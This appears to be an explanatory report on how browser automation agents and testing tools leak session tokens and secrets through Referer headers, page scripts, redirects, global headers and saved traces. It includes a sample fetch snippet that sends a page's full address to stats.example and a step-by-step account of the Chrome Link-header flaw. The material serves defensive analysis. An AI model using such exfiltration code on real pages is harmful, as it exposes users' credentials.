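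If a company points a subdomain such as `help.app.example` or `status.app.example` at an outside vendor, and its main site uses a permissive referrer policy, the vendor can receive full page addresses in Firefox and Safari as well as in Chromium.

Brave builds on Chromium but is stricter. According to Brave's *Referrer policy tests*, when a page uses the `unsafe-url` policy, another origin should receive only the page's origin while Shields, the browser's built-in blocker, is on. With Shields off, the other origin receives the full address, as in Chrome.

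An operator who runs agents on Firefox can also change the browser's default referrer policy with the preference `network.http.referer.defaultPolicy`, where 0 means `no-referrer`. The preference affects only pages that set no policy of their own. Playwright can drive Firefox and WebKit as well as Chromium, but its WebKit is a separate build from the Safari that people install, so a team should test that build's referrer behaviour before relying on it.

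### How many sites set a policy

Zagi and colleagues studied how many sites use referrer policies and whether scripts get round them. They drew 30,000 sites at random from a list of the million most popular and visited them in January 2024 with an automated browser, from San Francisco, Singapore and Amsterdam. The abstract reports 27,750 sites, but the results section reports 27,570. The figures below come from the San Francisco visit, which loaded 27,414 sites.

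The first column of figures counts sites where the researchers found a policy for a whole document. The second counts sites where the browser made at least one request under that policy. A site can appear in several rows.

| Policy | Document-wide policy found | At least one request under it |
|---|---|---|
| `no-referrer` | 7.39% | 9.56% |
| `same-origin` | 6.78% | 2.33% |
| `strict-origin` | 1.33% | 0.64% |
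| `strict-origin-when-cross-origin` | 27.14% | 100.00% |
| `origin` | 7.07% | 8.08% |
| `origin-when-cross-origin` | 8.21% | 5.41% |
| `no-referrer-when-downgrade` | 9.95% | 9.50% |
| `unsafe-url` | 4.48% | 5.26% |

Overall, 48.38% of sites had a document-wide policy. A response header appeared on 43.81% of sites and a meta tag on 11.09%. The header was much rarer in 2018, when a study by Lavrenovs and Melon, cited by Zagi and colleagues, found it in only 0.33% of HTTPS responses across a million sites. The two studies counted different things, so they do not give an exact growth rate.

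Element-level settings are less common. They appear on 13.39% of sites according to the abstract, but 17.19% according to the conclusion. Only 0.17% of the 33 million elements the researchers recorded had one.

The headline figure overstates how many site owners chose a policy, because it includes headers and tags from third parties. The researchers found `unsafe-url` headers in third-party responses on 891 sites, but in the site's own responses on only 112, about 0.4% of the total. A header on a third party's image or script does not change the policy of the page that loads it, though a header on a third-party frame does set the policy inside that frame.

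Two policies, `no-referrer-when-downgrade` and `unsafe-url`, send the full address to other HTTPS sites. The first applied to at least one request on 9.50% of sites and the second on 5.26%, so between 9.50% and 14.76% of sites had a request under at least one of them. Some of those requests came from third-party frames and carried the frame's address, which need not contain anything secret, so the share of sites that expose their own page addresses this way is probably lower.

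The crawler also followed ordinary links without logging in. It did not open reset links or private reports, so the figures don't measure how sites configure the pages where tokens appear. A site's reset page may have a stricter or looser policy than its news pages.

Other research suggests that how often the Referer header leaks data depends on where the data comes from. Zagi and colleagues cite a 2022 study of website search boxes by Kats and colleagues, in which 81.3% of sites passed users' search terms to third parties, usually through the Referer header. They also cite a 2021 study of sign-up forms on 307 shopping sites by Dao and Fukuda, in which 42% of sites exposed personal data to a third party. Of the sites that exposed data, 2.3% did so through the Referer header and 90.8% through the requested URL. This is probably because search terms usually appear in the address of the results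 page, while a name typed into a form usually does not appear in a page's address.

A strict referrer policy limits only what the browser puts in the Referer header. Scripts on the page can still read the address and send it themselves. This was the main reason third parties on 77.20% of the sites received all or part of the page's address in a request whose policy should have withheld it.

### Which agent actions send a Referer

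Browsers add a Referer when a document causes a request. Under W3C's procedure, a request with no document or script environment behind it has no referrer. So an agent that tells its browser to open an address directly normally sends no Referer with that first request. The main cases are these:

| What the agent does | Referer on the resulting request |
|---|---|
| Opens an address directly through its automation library | None, unless the tool sets one |
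| Clicks a link or submits a form | Current page's address, subject to the policy |
| Runs a script that sends the page to a new address | Current page's address, subject to the policy |
| Loads the images, scripts and frames on a page | That page's address, subject to the policy |
| Sends a request with curl or a few lines of Python | None, unless the code sets one |

When an agent clicks a link, the browser therefore sends the destination a Referer showing where the agent came from, but it sends none if the agent reads the link's address from the page's HTML and opens that address directly.

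When an agent opens an address directly, the browser doesn't send the previous page's address, but the new page's address can still leak. Suppose an agent opens a password reset link from an inbox in Chromium. The request for the reset page has no Referer. The page then loads a font, an analytics script and a logo from three other companies, and each of those requests can carry a Referer based on the reset page's address. If the page's referrer policy allows the full address to be sent, all three companies receive the reset code in it without the agent clicking anything on the page.

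A fresh browser profile can increase the number of requests that send a Referer to other sites, because its cache is empty. The browser has to request every third-party file, while a regular visitor's browser may already have some stored. A testing agent that starts a new profile for each of 200 test runs can therefore send the Referer 200 times.

When a request is redirected, its Referer header comes from the page where the navigation began, never from the address that did the redirecting. SiteMinder's redirect is therefore unlikely to leak its session value through a Referer header. An OAuth code is more exposed if the provider redirects the browser to an address that displays a page, because that page's address contains the code and the page's requests for other files can include that address in their Referer headers.

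A server can also send a new referrer policy with a redirect, and the browser applies that policy to the next request. Suppose the agent clicks a link to `https://app.example/out`, which redirects to a partner site. The request to `/out` stays on the same origin, so under the default policy its Referer header contains the full address of the page the agent was on. If the redirect sets `unsafe-url`, Chromium sends that full address to the partner. Chromium's tests check the Referer on ordinary links, links that open a new tab, and redirects between HTTP and HTTPS.

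Automation tools can set the Referer header themselves. In Playwright, the `goto` command, which opens an address, accepts an optional `referer` value. Puppeteer, a similar library from Google's Chrome team, accepts both a Referer and a referrer policy. Testers use these options to check, for example, how a site treats visitors who arrive from a search engine. But a framework that automatically fills in the previous page's address, to make an agent look like a person clicking through a site, would reintroduce the leak, because the previous page's policy does not necessarily trim a value that a tool supplies.

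Playwright can also add fixed headers to every request a page makes. If these include a Referer, third parties may receive it, so it should never contain an address that includes a token.

### The Chrome flaw of May 2025

In May 2025, Google fixed a flaw in Chrome that let a third party get the full address of a page even when the page's policy should have withheld it. The flaw, CVE-2025-4664, was in the Loader, the part of Chrome that fetches files. It had been public since 5 May, according to Help Net Security's *CISA* (2025), and Google credited a post on X by security researcher Vsevolod Kokorin.

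The flaw involved the Link header. A server can add this header to a response to make the browser fetch another file early, and the header can include a referrer policy for that fetch. WHATWG's HTML standard provides for this in the response that delivers a document, where the site's own server sets the policy for its page. But Chrome also processed Link headers in responses to subresource requests, according to Kokorin's explanation in SC Media's *Google Chrome data leakage bug confirmed as actively exploited*. Outside companies that served files to the page could therefore influence the policy.

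Suppose an OAuth sign-in ends at `https://client.example/redirection_endpoint?code=abcd`. The page uses the default policy and includes an image from stats.example. The attack would go like this:

1. Chrome requests the image. It correctly sends only `https://client.example/` in the Referer header.
2. Stats.example returns the image with a Link header. The header makes Chrome fetch a second file from stats.example under the policy `unsafe-url`.
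3. Chrome sends the second request as if the page itself had asked for the file under that policy. The Referer now contains the full address, including the code.

A redirect from stats.example would not have exposed the page's full address. Under W3C's procedure, the browser reuses the Referer it already shortened for the first request, so a looser policy on the redirect can't restore the missing part. With the Link header, Chrome made a new request and started again from the full address.

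Kokorin warned that in OAuth sign-ins the leak might lead to an account takeover. The attack would work only if the site does not use PKCE and displays the page before redeeming the code. Long-lived share links and session tokens in the query are at greater risk because they keep working.

MITRE (2025) describes an attacker using a "crafted HTML page", and Help Net Security also says the victim would have to open a malicious page. Kokorin's account is more worrying for agents. He stresses that a third-party image is enough, which developers rarely consider. An attacker who can place an image in a comment, chat message or support ticket might therefore get the address of any page that displays it.

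Google rated the severity as high, but the MITRE record also has a score of 4.3 out of 10, or medium, based on a low loss of confidentiality. That score is too low for a page with a live session token in its query string.

It was also unclear whether anyone had used the flaw. Help Net Security quotes Google as saying that "knowledge of CVE-2025-4664" existed in the wild, which could mean only that people were discussing it. A software maintainer's note on updating a Chromium package (emilylange, *chromium,chromedriver*) repeats a stronger statement, that there were reports of an exploit in the wild. On 15 May, the US cybersecurity agency CISA (2025) added the flaw to its catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to exploit. News reports then described the attacks as confirmed.

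CISA reversed this on 5 June. It said it had learned that the flaw "has not been exploited" and that it would remove the entry. The vulnerability record now lists exploitation as "none". The earlier articles remain online, so an operator who searches for the flaw may still read that criminals used it.

Google fixed the flaw in version 136.0.7103.113. The flaw also affected other browsers built on Chromium, according to *Chromium-based Browser Active Exploit Vulnerability* (2025), an advisory from WA SOC, the Western Australian government's security team. Microsoft fixed it in Edge. Mozilla's *Full referrer URL exposed even from websites using strict referrer policies* describes a related earlier bug in Firefox, CVE-2021-23971, which exposed full addresses even on sites that had set `no-referrer`.

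The rules published by W3C and WHATWG may not fully settle how browsers should treat a referrer policy in a Link header on a subresource. Firefox's source code, as indexed by Searchfox, includes a test that expects browsers to ignore the policy, but the test's file name still marks it as tentative.

Most people got the fix through an automatic update, but an agent's browser often doesn't update itself. Each Playwright release works with particular browser builds, and teams commonly store the library and browser together in a container image so that every test runs the same way. The browser then stays at the same version until someone rebuilds the image. Packaged copies of Chromium also need a separate update. For example, emilylange's change moved one from version 136.0.7103.92 to 136.0.7103.113 and replaced the checksums that identify its files.

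An image built in April 2025 and not rebuilt since still has the flaw, regardless of the policies set by the sites it visits. It also lacks every later security fix. By June 2026, stable Chrome had reached version 149, and Google's *Stable Channel Update for Desktop* (2026) lists 28 security fixes in a single update. Playwright can report the version of the browser it is driving, so a team can check it at the start of each run and stop the run if the version is lower than 136.0.7103.113.

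## How do scripts on the page pass on the address when the Referer header is restricted?

A script running on a page can read the page's address and send it in the query or body of its own request, where the referrer policy has no effect. Analytics and advertising scripts routinely do this, and they run in an agent's browser even when the agent has no cookies.

### What a script on the page can read

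In the earlier example, the report page at app.example loaded an image from stats.example. Analytics companies often ask sites to include a script as well:

`<script src="https://stats.example/tag.js"></script>`

The browser downloads this file from stats.example but runs it as part of app.example's page. *Same-Origin Policy*, a chapter of UC Berkeley's CS 161 security textbook, explains that JavaScript runs with the origin of the page that loads it, while a frame keeps the origin of the server it came from. A script from stats.example can therefore read the page's address through the `location.href` property, but a frame from stats.example can't.

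Suppose app.example sets the policy `strict-origin`, and an agent opens `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN#totals`. The script could run this code:

```
fetch("https://stats.example/collect", {
  method: "POST",
  body: "page=" + encodeURIComponent(location.href)
});
```

The browser then sends something like this:

```
POST /collect HTTP/1.1
Host: stats.example
Referer: https://app.example/
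Content-Type: text/plain;charset=UTF-8

page=https%3A%2F%2Fapp.example%2Freport%3Fsession%3DTOKEN%23totals
```

The Referer header contains only the origin, as the policy requires, but the request body contains the whole address, including the fragment. Under `no-referrer`, the browser would omit the header and still send the same body. This is a simple request, so it needs no preflight.

Site owners have little control over what an included script may read. In *SoK*, Sprecher, Kerschbaumer and Kirda call access control for third-party scripts "all or nothing" and say it has been that way for over a decade. Drakonakis, Ioannidis and Polakis (2025) write in *Dredging the River Styx* that existing defences cannot reliably distinguish a site's own scripts from embedded third-party ones.

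Some designers put a secret in the fragment to keep it out of the Referer header, as Claude.ai did with its emailed sign-in links. Tennison warns that third-party scripts on the page can still read the fragment. She also describes `replaceState()`, which lets a page replace the address in the location bar with one that lacks the secret, but this hides the secret only from scripts that start after the swap. Tennison also advises restoring the original address when the visitor leaves, so that the Back button works. A script that sends a last report at that moment might pick up the secret.

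The token can also leak from the next page. Scripts there can read `document.referrer`, which holds as much of the previous page's address as the referrer policy allows. Under the default policy, that is the full address if both pages share an origin. If the agent clicks from the report to `https://app.example/help`, a script on the help page can read the report's address, including the token, even if the report page has no third-party scripts. A stricter referrer policy does prevent this.

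Google's *[GA4] Data redaction* lists Google Analytics event parameters for the addresses of the current page, the previous page, the target of a link and the destination of a form. A site owner can make the browser remove query parameters before it sends the data, but only those the owner lists by name. If the owner lists only `email` and `firstname`, the browser still sends Google the value of `session`. The feature removes only email addresses and the listed query parameters, so it leaves a reset code in the path.

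### How many sites let scripts get round the policy

Zagi and colleagues measured how often third parties received an address that the referrer policy should have withheld. Their crawler recorded each request's URL, headers and body, and the referrer policy the browser applied. They split each page's address into its parts and searched every third-party request for those parts, undoing up to two layers of encoding such as Base64.

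The researchers counted a circumvention when the policy allowed only the origin, or nothing, and the request still contained the page's path or query. They ignored paths and queries of ten characters or fewer, because short strings can match by chance. They checked 100 cases with the full address by hand and found no false positives, then checked 100 cases with only the path or query and found 12.

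On the visit from San Francisco, 21,164 of 27,414 sites (77.20%) had circumventions. All but 80 of those sites had at least one case involving the full address, so the weaker partial matches barely affect the total. The rates from Singapore and Amsterdam were within a percentage point of that. Scripts put the address in the requested URL on 74.78% of sites and in the request body on 32.57%.

On 9.15% of sites, the Referer header still contained the page's address. A script on the page had added the address to the URL of a third-party frame. When the frame loaded its own files, the browser sent the frame's URL as the referrer, with the page's address inside it. For example, a travel blog's full page address reached the ferry-booking site ferryscanner.com this way, although the blog's policy allowed sending only the origin.

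The table shows eight of the ten companies that received addresses on the most sites.

| Company | Sites that contacted it | Sites that sent it an address despite the policy |
|---|---|---|
| Google | 24,120 | 18,317 (75.94%) |
| Facebook | 8,992 | 6,573 (73.10%) |
| Microsoft | 5,818 | 3,721 (63.96%) |
| Yandex | 1,340 | 1,221 (91.12%) |
| Twitter | 1,741 | 1,151 (66.11%) |
| ByteDance (TikTok) | 1,121 | 996 (88.85%) |
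| Pinterest | 1,047 | 911 (87.01%) |
| HubSpot | 1,009 | 707 (70.07%) |

Google therefore received addresses in this way on about two thirds of all the sites in the crawl.

Many site owners install these scripts to learn which pages people visit, so "circumvention" is not necessarily an attack. The researchers call the result "by design", because the browser gives an included script the same rights as the site's own code. They note that some developers expect a restrictive referrer policy to apply to scripts.

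The rate was 11.75% among sites with requests under `no-referrer`, compared with 65.14% for `strict-origin`. Scripts can still read the page's address under `no-referrer`. However, sites often set that policy on individual script and stylesheet elements, and stylesheet requests rarely have a reason to contain the address.

Third-party scripts read `location.href` on 89.63% of sites and `location.hash`, which holds the fragment, on 71.49%. A script can read a fragment for harmless reasons, such as scrolling to the right place, so the sites that exposed fragments to outside code did not necessarily leak them.

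### What chatbot websites send

Many chatbots give each conversation its own address, such as `claude.ai/chat/` followed by an identifier. In *Tracking Conversations*, Jazlan, Wang and colleagues (2026) tested whether 20 popular chatbots passed these addresses to other companies. For each chatbot, they created a new account, opened the site in Chrome with a fresh browser state, entered the prompt "pregnancy test near me" and recorded the traffic until the answer was complete.

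They then searched the traffic for the prompt, the conversation's web address and identifier, and the test user's name and email. They undid common encodings and compression and also looked for hashed forms. Zagi and colleagues had left out hashes because nobody can open a hashed web address, but an advertiser can still use a hashed email address by matching it with the same hash from another site.

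Seventeen of the 20 chatbots shared something with at least one third party. The other three, Gemini, Meta AI and Duck.ai, contacted only domains belonging to their own companies. Gemini used Google Analytics, but the researchers did not count Google as a third party there.

Fifteen chatbots shared conversation addresses or identifiers with a total of 29 destinations. According to the study's breakdown, all 15 shared an identifier and ten shared a complete address. The 15 include Gemini, although the study says it contacted no third parties, so a strict count would be 14.

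In most cases the chatbots' developers probably didn't choose to share conversation addresses, because tags (small scripts that report visits) from Meta, Google and Microsoft's Bing collect the current page's address by default. SeaArt sent conversation identifiers to 12 destinations, Genspark to seven, and the others to between one and four.

Genspark, SeaArt and ChatOn also sent readable text from the conversation to Microsoft Clarity, a session-replay tool that records what a page displays so that the site's owner can play the visit back. Such a tool could also record a secret shown on the page, like a new API key or a share link, even if the page's address doesn't contain one.

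Some of this traffic goes to the site's own domain. Microsoft Copilot sent its Clarity data to copilot.microsoft.com. ChatGPT sent chatgpt.com data with fields used by Datadog and Statsig, which provide monitoring and product-testing tools. A tester who searches an agent's network log only for other companies' domains would miss these requests.

Jazlan and colleagues also tested private or temporary chats on the chatbots that offered them. They found no conversation or identity data going to third parties from these chats.

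### When a conversation's address opens the conversation

A company that receives a conversation's address can open the conversation only if the server requires nothing else. If the server also requires the owner's login, the company can use the address only to group events from the same conversation. The company may still be able to link those events to a person through a cookie or a hashed email address.

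IMDEA Networks' *Your conversations with AI may not be as private as you think* (2026) presents LeakyLM, a study of ChatGPT, Claude, Grok and Perplexity by the institute's researchers. By default, anyone with the link could open a Grok conversation, or a Perplexity conversation if the user had no account. Only the owner could open a signed-in user's Perplexity conversation, or any ChatGPT or Claude conversation, unless the owner shared it.

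According to IMDEA Networks, Grok and Perplexity sent these links to trackers such as Meta's. Perplexity had stopped using Meta's tracker by 3 April 2026. Perplexity's addresses also contained up to about 30 characters of the user's first question, so they could reveal the topic even when the link didn't open.

The blogger ndurner objects in *LeakyLM* that the announcement covers four assistants, although a leaked link could give access to a conversation only on Grok and in some Perplexity configurations. The study's findings on default access support this objection. The researchers also had no evidence that any tracking company had opened a conversation.

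Even an open conversation link usually gives much less access than a session token. The holder can read one conversation but can't act as the user. Leaking the link is more serious if the user pasted a password or API key into the chat.

### Agents that browse without cookies

An agent that opens a password reset link in a fresh browser profile runs the page's scripts just as a person's browser would. Those scripts can read the address without a cookie, so they can send it on the first visit, before any login.

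Refusing cookies in a consent banner may make little difference. Zagi and colleagues visited 100 sites from Amsterdam three times. They found circumventions on 72 sites when the crawler ignored the banner, 74 when it refused consent and 79 when it accepted. The sample is small, and some of the difference may come from ordinary changes between visits.

Agents may also load more tracking scripts than a simple crawler. In *Beyond the Landing Page*, Sakib, Akram and colleagues (2026) compared an agent built on the browser-use framework with a scripted Chromium browser that visited the same addresses. Both browsed without logging in. Across 11,435 matching pages, the agent recorded trackers from an average of 6.00 organisations per page, compared with 4.01 for the scripted browser.

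Consent banners seem to explain part of the gap. In a separate run on 445 sites, the researchers told the agent to dismiss anything covering the page. It clicked an explicit "accept" button 201 times and a "reject" button once. On the sites where they could compare the two kinds of click, scripts from an average of 9.2 new third-party domains loaded within ten seconds of a confirmed consent click, compared with 1.0 after an ordinary click that loaded a page. If the page's address contains a token, each of those scripts can read it.

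The time an agent spends on a page may matter too. On pages that human participants also visited, the agent recorded 1.71 times as many tracker organisations as the participants did. When the researchers shortened the agent's visits to match theirs, the ratio fell to 0.95. An agent that leaves a reset page open while its model generates the next action may therefore give more scripts time to load.

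Sakib and colleagues used one small open model and counted trackers, not leaked addresses. None of the three measurement studies followed a live login token, so the 77.20% figure isn't an estimate for password reset pages. Some sites leave analytics off those pages, while others load the same scripts on every page through a shared template.

A plain HTTP client such as curl avoids this route because it doesn't run scripts. A browser usually avoids it too when a signed link returns an image or a PDF, because there is no web page for a third-party script to run in. However, some reset and sign-in pages build their forms with JavaScript, so an agent that fetches one with curl may get an almost empty page and have to open the link in a browser.

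## How does an agent pass on a token when no one is attacking it?

An agent can send a token to another company just by using its tools. It may give a URL containing the token to an outside service, follow a redirect to a different host, or put the token in a header that its browser sends with every request. It also leaves copies of URLs in logs, test reports and the conversation it sends to its model's provider.

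### Giving the address to another service

An agent that can't run a page's JavaScript may use a page reader, an outside service that opens a page in its own browser and returns the text. Some readers take the target's address as part of their own:

`https://reader.example/https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN`

When an agent asks a reader service to fetch a URL that contains a token, the service's server receives the token and uses it to open the page. The agent gets the text it wanted, so nothing looks wrong. The service's browser also loads the page's images and runs its scripts, so the URL can reach the analytics companies the page uses. Screenshot services work in much the same way. The agent's cookie and referrer settings have no effect here because the agent put the URL in the request.

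An agent can also leak a token by pasting a link it can't open into a search engine. The token usually ends up in the URL of the results page, where that page's scripts can read it.

An agent that checks a link before opening it may send it to a malware scanner, and some scanners publish what people submit. An agent that saves a page as evidence may ask a web archive to copy it. The archived copy can remain readable even after the owner revokes the link.

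### What researchers found in public URL repositories

Scanners and archives hold many such addresses. For *The Silent Spill* (2026), Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues collected 6,094,475 URLs between January and April 2025 from three scanning services (URLScan.io, VirusTotal and Hybrid Analysis), the Wayback Machine web archive, and sites where people paste text to share it. URLScan.io supplied about 90% of them.

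The researchers then narrowed the collection in stages:

| Step | URLs left |
|---|---|
| Collect from the five sources | 6,094,475 |
| Remove stylesheets, fonts, most images and similar files | 4,982,613 |
| Keep URLs whose path or query matches one of 302 terms, such as `token` or `invoice` | 2,104,376 |
| Apply tests of length, nesting and number of parameters | 832,714 |
| Keep pages that still load without an error or a login demand | 149,450 |
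| Keep pages whose contents match one of 402 terms and pass further checks | 12,331 |

In the last step, a browser loaded each page for five seconds, and the system searched the visible text, form fields and metadata. It also used text recognition on some images.

The 12,331 results are potential leaks, about 0.2% of the collection. The largest category, authentication and tokens, had 5,343. The more serious finds included 26 password reset links, 83 API keys, 12 open contract-signing sessions and 62 URLs with login tokens that lasted for days or never expired.

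The researchers estimated the error rate by inspecting random samples from eight categories by hand. They rejected 28 of 232 URLs as false positives, including 3 of the 30 in the authentication category. Because 30 is a small sample, they calculated a 95% Wilson interval, a range of plausible values for the true rate, which ran from 3.5% to 26%. Even at 26%, 3,954 of the 5,343 authentication matches would be correct.

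The number of working credentials is probably lower than 3,954, because the researchers counted an exposed invoice number or identifier as a true positive. Their list of terms also included common names for anti-forgery tokens, which are useless without the user's session.

The study calls the 26 reset links live, but the researchers opened the pages without submitting anything or trying to reset a password. They had first tested 24 patterns of reset and backup-code links on their own accounts and found that a visit did not cancel the code. A scanner can therefore open a reset link and leave it working for the next person who reads the scan report. The total of 26 is hard to reconcile with the study's description of VirusTotal's 1,445 potential leaks as mainly password reset links.

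The researchers revisited 2,000 flagged URLs after 75 days and could still reach 762 of them (38%) without logging in. They may have missed links that worked only briefly, because they discarded 683,264 URLs at the availability check, and some of those probably worked when a scanner first published them. Someone who watched new reports as they appeared could have used those links before they stopped working.

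Ramadan and colleagues measured repositories, not agents, and did not identify who submitted each URL. They note that email providers and company security gateways often forward links to scanners automatically. They also chose search terms and domains to find sensitive material, so the 0.2% figure does not apply to links in general. Their study is useful to an agent's operator because it shows that strangers can look up a submitted link and often still open it months later.

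### When a redirect changes the host

When a server redirects a request, it puts the new address in a `Location` header. Browsers follow redirects automatically, and curl does so when the user adds the `--location` option.

Suppose an operator allows an agent to contact api.app.example. The agent uses curl to request a report and attaches three credentials:

```
GET /reports/88 HTTP/1.1
Host: api.app.example
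Authorization: Bearer TOKEN-A
Cookie: session=TOKEN-B
X-Api-Key: TOKEN-C
```

The application keeps its files with a storage company, so it replies:

```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://files.example/88.pdf?sig=TOKEN-D
```

A current version of curl then sends this:

```
GET /88.pdf?sig=TOKEN-D HTTP/1.1
Host: files.example
X-Api-Key: TOKEN-C
```

The storage company needs TOKEN-D, the signature on the file link, but not TOKEN-C, which may give access to the application's entire API.

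When a redirect leads to another host, libcurl has withheld the Authorization header since version 7.58.0 and the Cookie header since 7.64.0, unless the developer overrides this, according to its manual. It still sends all other custom headers to the new host. The manual page for the command-line tool includes a warning about combining sensitive headers with redirects.

Clients often pass API key headers on to a new host because they recognise credentials by the header's name. Authorization and Cookie have standard meanings, but each company names its own key header, so a client can't tell from the name alone whether the new host needs it.

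In April 2026, NVD, the US government's vulnerability database, published a record of this fault in follow-redirects, a library that handles redirects for Node.js programs. GCVE's *GHSA-R4Q5-VMMM-2653* (2026) adds that axios, a widely used HTTP client, depends on the library. NVD's record also lists affected Red Hat products, including two versions of OpenShift AI, a platform for running AI models.

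OpenClaw, an assistant that people run on their own computers, had the same fault in the function it uses to fetch URLs. OSV's *GHSA-6mgf-v5j7-45cr* (2026) rates the fault's severity 9.3 out of 10. The developers replaced their list of headers to drop with a list of harmless headers to keep.

| Client | Headers it drops when the host or origin changes | Headers it passes on |
|---|---|---|
| curl since 7.64.0 | Authorization, Cookie | Other custom headers |
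| follow-redirects before 1.16.0 | Authorization, Proxy-Authorization, Cookie | Custom headers such as X-API-Key and X-Auth-Token |
| OpenClaw up to 2026.3.2 | Authorization, Proxy-Authorization, Cookie, Cookie2 | Custom headers such as X-Api-Key and Private-Token |
| OpenClaw from 2026.3.7 | Everything not on its list of harmless headers | Headers for content type preferences and caching |

The OpenClaw advisory describes a remote service that triggers a redirect to collect keys. The same leak happens without bad intent whenever an API redirects downloads to a storage company, as in the example above.

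Fixing one function may not fix the whole program. Less than a month after the first advisory, OSV's *GHSA-68v4-hmwv-f43h* (2026) reported that OpenClaw's media downloads still kept the Authorization header when a redirect led to another origin. A few days later, GitLab's *GHSA-qx8j-g322-qj6m* (2026) reported that the function from the first advisory could also resend request bodies. Redirects with status codes 307 and 308 tell a client to repeat the original request with its body, which contains the password if the request was a login.

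Scripts in a web page have more protection. Under WHATWG's Fetch standard, a browser drops the Authorization header when a redirect leads to another origin, and it sends a custom header to the new server only if that server allows it in a preflight response.

None of these rules affects a token in the redirect address itself. Suppose a company moves its reports to an outside vendor and sets up a redirect that copies the old path and query:

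`https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` → `https://vendor.example/report?session=TOKEN`

The vendor receives the session token in the first line of the request, even from a client that drops every header.

When a server redirects a request, the browser carries the original URL's fragment over to the new address unless the Location header has its own fragment. For example, if an agent opens `https://app.example/login#key=TOKEN` and the server redirects to `https://partner.example/welcome`, the browser ends up at `https://partner.example/welcome#key=TOKEN`, where scripts on the partner's page can read the token.

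The agent may also fail to notice that it has moved to a different host. In *How Aikido secures AI pentesting agents by design*, Shah writes that some of the security company's testing agents reach an outside site such as Reddit and assume they are still on the site they were testing. An agent that makes this mistake could type its test login into the wrong site's form. Shah also describes an agent that would have reached production servers through an application if Aikido's network controls had not blocked the request. Aikido is describing its own product here and does not report how often either problem occurs.

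Some limits on where an agent may go don't cover redirects. Playwright MCP, which lets a language model drive a browser through Playwright, has an option that lists the origins the browser may contact. According to Playwright's documentation, this list is not a security boundary and does not affect redirects.

### Headers that go to every host

A test browser can send a secret to other companies without any redirect. Staging servers and preview sites often require a secret header, which testers commonly supply through a setting that adds it to the browser's requests.

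In Playwright, that setting applies to all hosts. Playwright's *BrowserContext* page says the extra headers go with every request from any page in the browser session. Puppeteer's *Page.setExtraHTTPHeaders() method* describes the same behaviour for a single page. Testing products built on these libraries can behave the same way. Octomind, for example, lets users set Playwright's extra headers for a whole project and sends them with every request.

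If a tester sets an Authorization header this way and opens app.example's report page, the browser also sends the token with its request for the image on stats.example. This can happen even when the page's address contains no secret and the referrer policy is strict.

GitLab's *Restrict sending custom request headers to allowed hosts* describes a possible token leak by the company's security scanner, which opens customers' sites in Chrome to look for vulnerabilities. In October 2022, GitLab's developers found a customer's log in which Chrome was requesting a stylesheet from use.fontawesome.com, a host for icon fonts, with the customer's bearer token in the Authorization header. The log records the request as Chrome prepared it, so it does not prove that the token arrived. If Chrome had sent a preflight request first and Font Awesome's server had refused the header, Chrome would not have sent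 the token. The developers concluded that tokens might leak and planned to limit custom headers to approved hosts.

A team can discover that its tests are sending a header to outside services when one of them refuses a preflight request. On DEV Community, a developer describes adding a harmless header to Playwright's configuration to mark test traffic. The browser also attached it to requests to Ably, which ran the app's live messaging, and to Supabase and analytics services. The developer noticed because the header triggered a preflight, which was refused, and live messaging stopped working. If every service had accepted the header, the tests would have passed and the developer might never have known.

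Other tools behave similarly. In *Basic auth is sent to subsequent domains as well*, a user on WebPageTest's forum asked why the speed-testing service sent a site's login header to another company's file server. The reply confirmed that the service added the header to all requests and could not restrict it to certain origins. In *Scoping auth tokens in headless Chrome with an MV3 extension*, the engineer herohua found the same problem when using Chrome to turn private documentation pages into PDFs. The problem wasn't visible in the PDFs, which looked perfect.

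#### Preview sites

The hosting company Vercel protects preview copies of unreleased sites with a login, which automated tools generally can't complete. A team can create a bypass secret for the tool to send with each request instead of logging in, in a header or a query parameter named `x-vercel-protection-bypass`.

Vercel's *Automated & Agent Access*, last updated in September 2026, recommends sending the secret in a header rather than in the URL, because proxies and servers often log URLs. Its Playwright example puts the secret in the global header setting. According to Playwright, this may send the secret to every third party whose files the preview loads.

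According to Vercel's troubleshooting advice, a browser run by Playwright sends the header only when it first loads a page, not when a test clicks a link. That fits Vercel's example for Cypress, another testing tool, which attaches the header to a single command. But it conflicts with Playwright's documentation, which the DEV Community developer's experience supports.

A token in a query parameter appears in the page's address, where scripts can read it and a loose referrer policy can expose it. The browser does not send it to every host, as it does a global header. Under the default policy, a preview with a third-party font and no third-party scripts would leak the header but not the parameter. If the preview has an analytics script, the vendor could receive either one.

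Vercel suggests the parameter for services that can't set headers, such as Slack, Stripe and GitHub when they notify an application of events. A developer gives the service an address like this:

`https://your-app.vercel.app/api/slack/events?x-vercel-protection-bypass=SECRET`

Slack then holds the secret and sends it with every notification. According to Vercel's *Protection Bypass for Automation*, each secret opens all of a project's deployments until someone revokes it, so a secret created for one Slack address also opens every other preview in the project. The secret also bypasses the firewall's normal blocking and bot checks, but it does not log anyone in to the application itself.

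Testing companies may need the secret too. QA.tech's *Vercel Preview* tells customers to supply one so its tests can open protected previews. Vercel advises teams to create a separate secret for each tool so they can cancel one without disrupting the rest.

### Copies that the agent leaves behind

An agent that contacts only the right host can still leave the full URL, including any token in it, in several places where other people and companies can read it.

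An agent usually sends the first copy of a token to the model's provider. Agent frameworks pass the current URL to the model and generally resend the whole conversation at every step. If a reset link appears in the result of step 3 of a 40-step run, the provider receives it at each of the 37 later steps, unless the framework trims old results.

Testing tools also keep recordings, such as Playwright traces, which let a developer replay a test step by step. Currents, a company that sells a dashboard for Playwright tests, explains that a trace archive holds copies of the page along with request and response headers and bodies, so it can include bearer tokens and newly issued cookies as well as URLs. Teams often record a trace only when a failed test is retried, which is also when someone is most likely to attach it to a bug report.

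These recordings can last longer than the people who made them expect. Playwright's *Setting up CI* describes a workflow that its installer can add to a GitHub project. The workflow runs the tests on every change to the main branch, uploads the report even if tests fail, and keeps it for 30 days. A signed file link that lasts seven days will expire before the report is deleted, but a Vercel bypass secret will still work. The guide also shows how to publish reports at a public web address. Elsewhere in its documentation, Playwright warns that traces and console logs can contain access tokens, and tells teams to encrypt them or upload them only to trusted storage.

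Some tools now remove secrets before saving or sharing a recording. *Test Replay now redacts sensitive network data before upload* announces that Cypress recordings hide credential-like values by default, which matters because everyone with access to the project can view the network log. Playwright MCP lets an operator list secret values in a file and removes matching text from what the model sees, though Playwright calls this "a convenience, not a security boundary".

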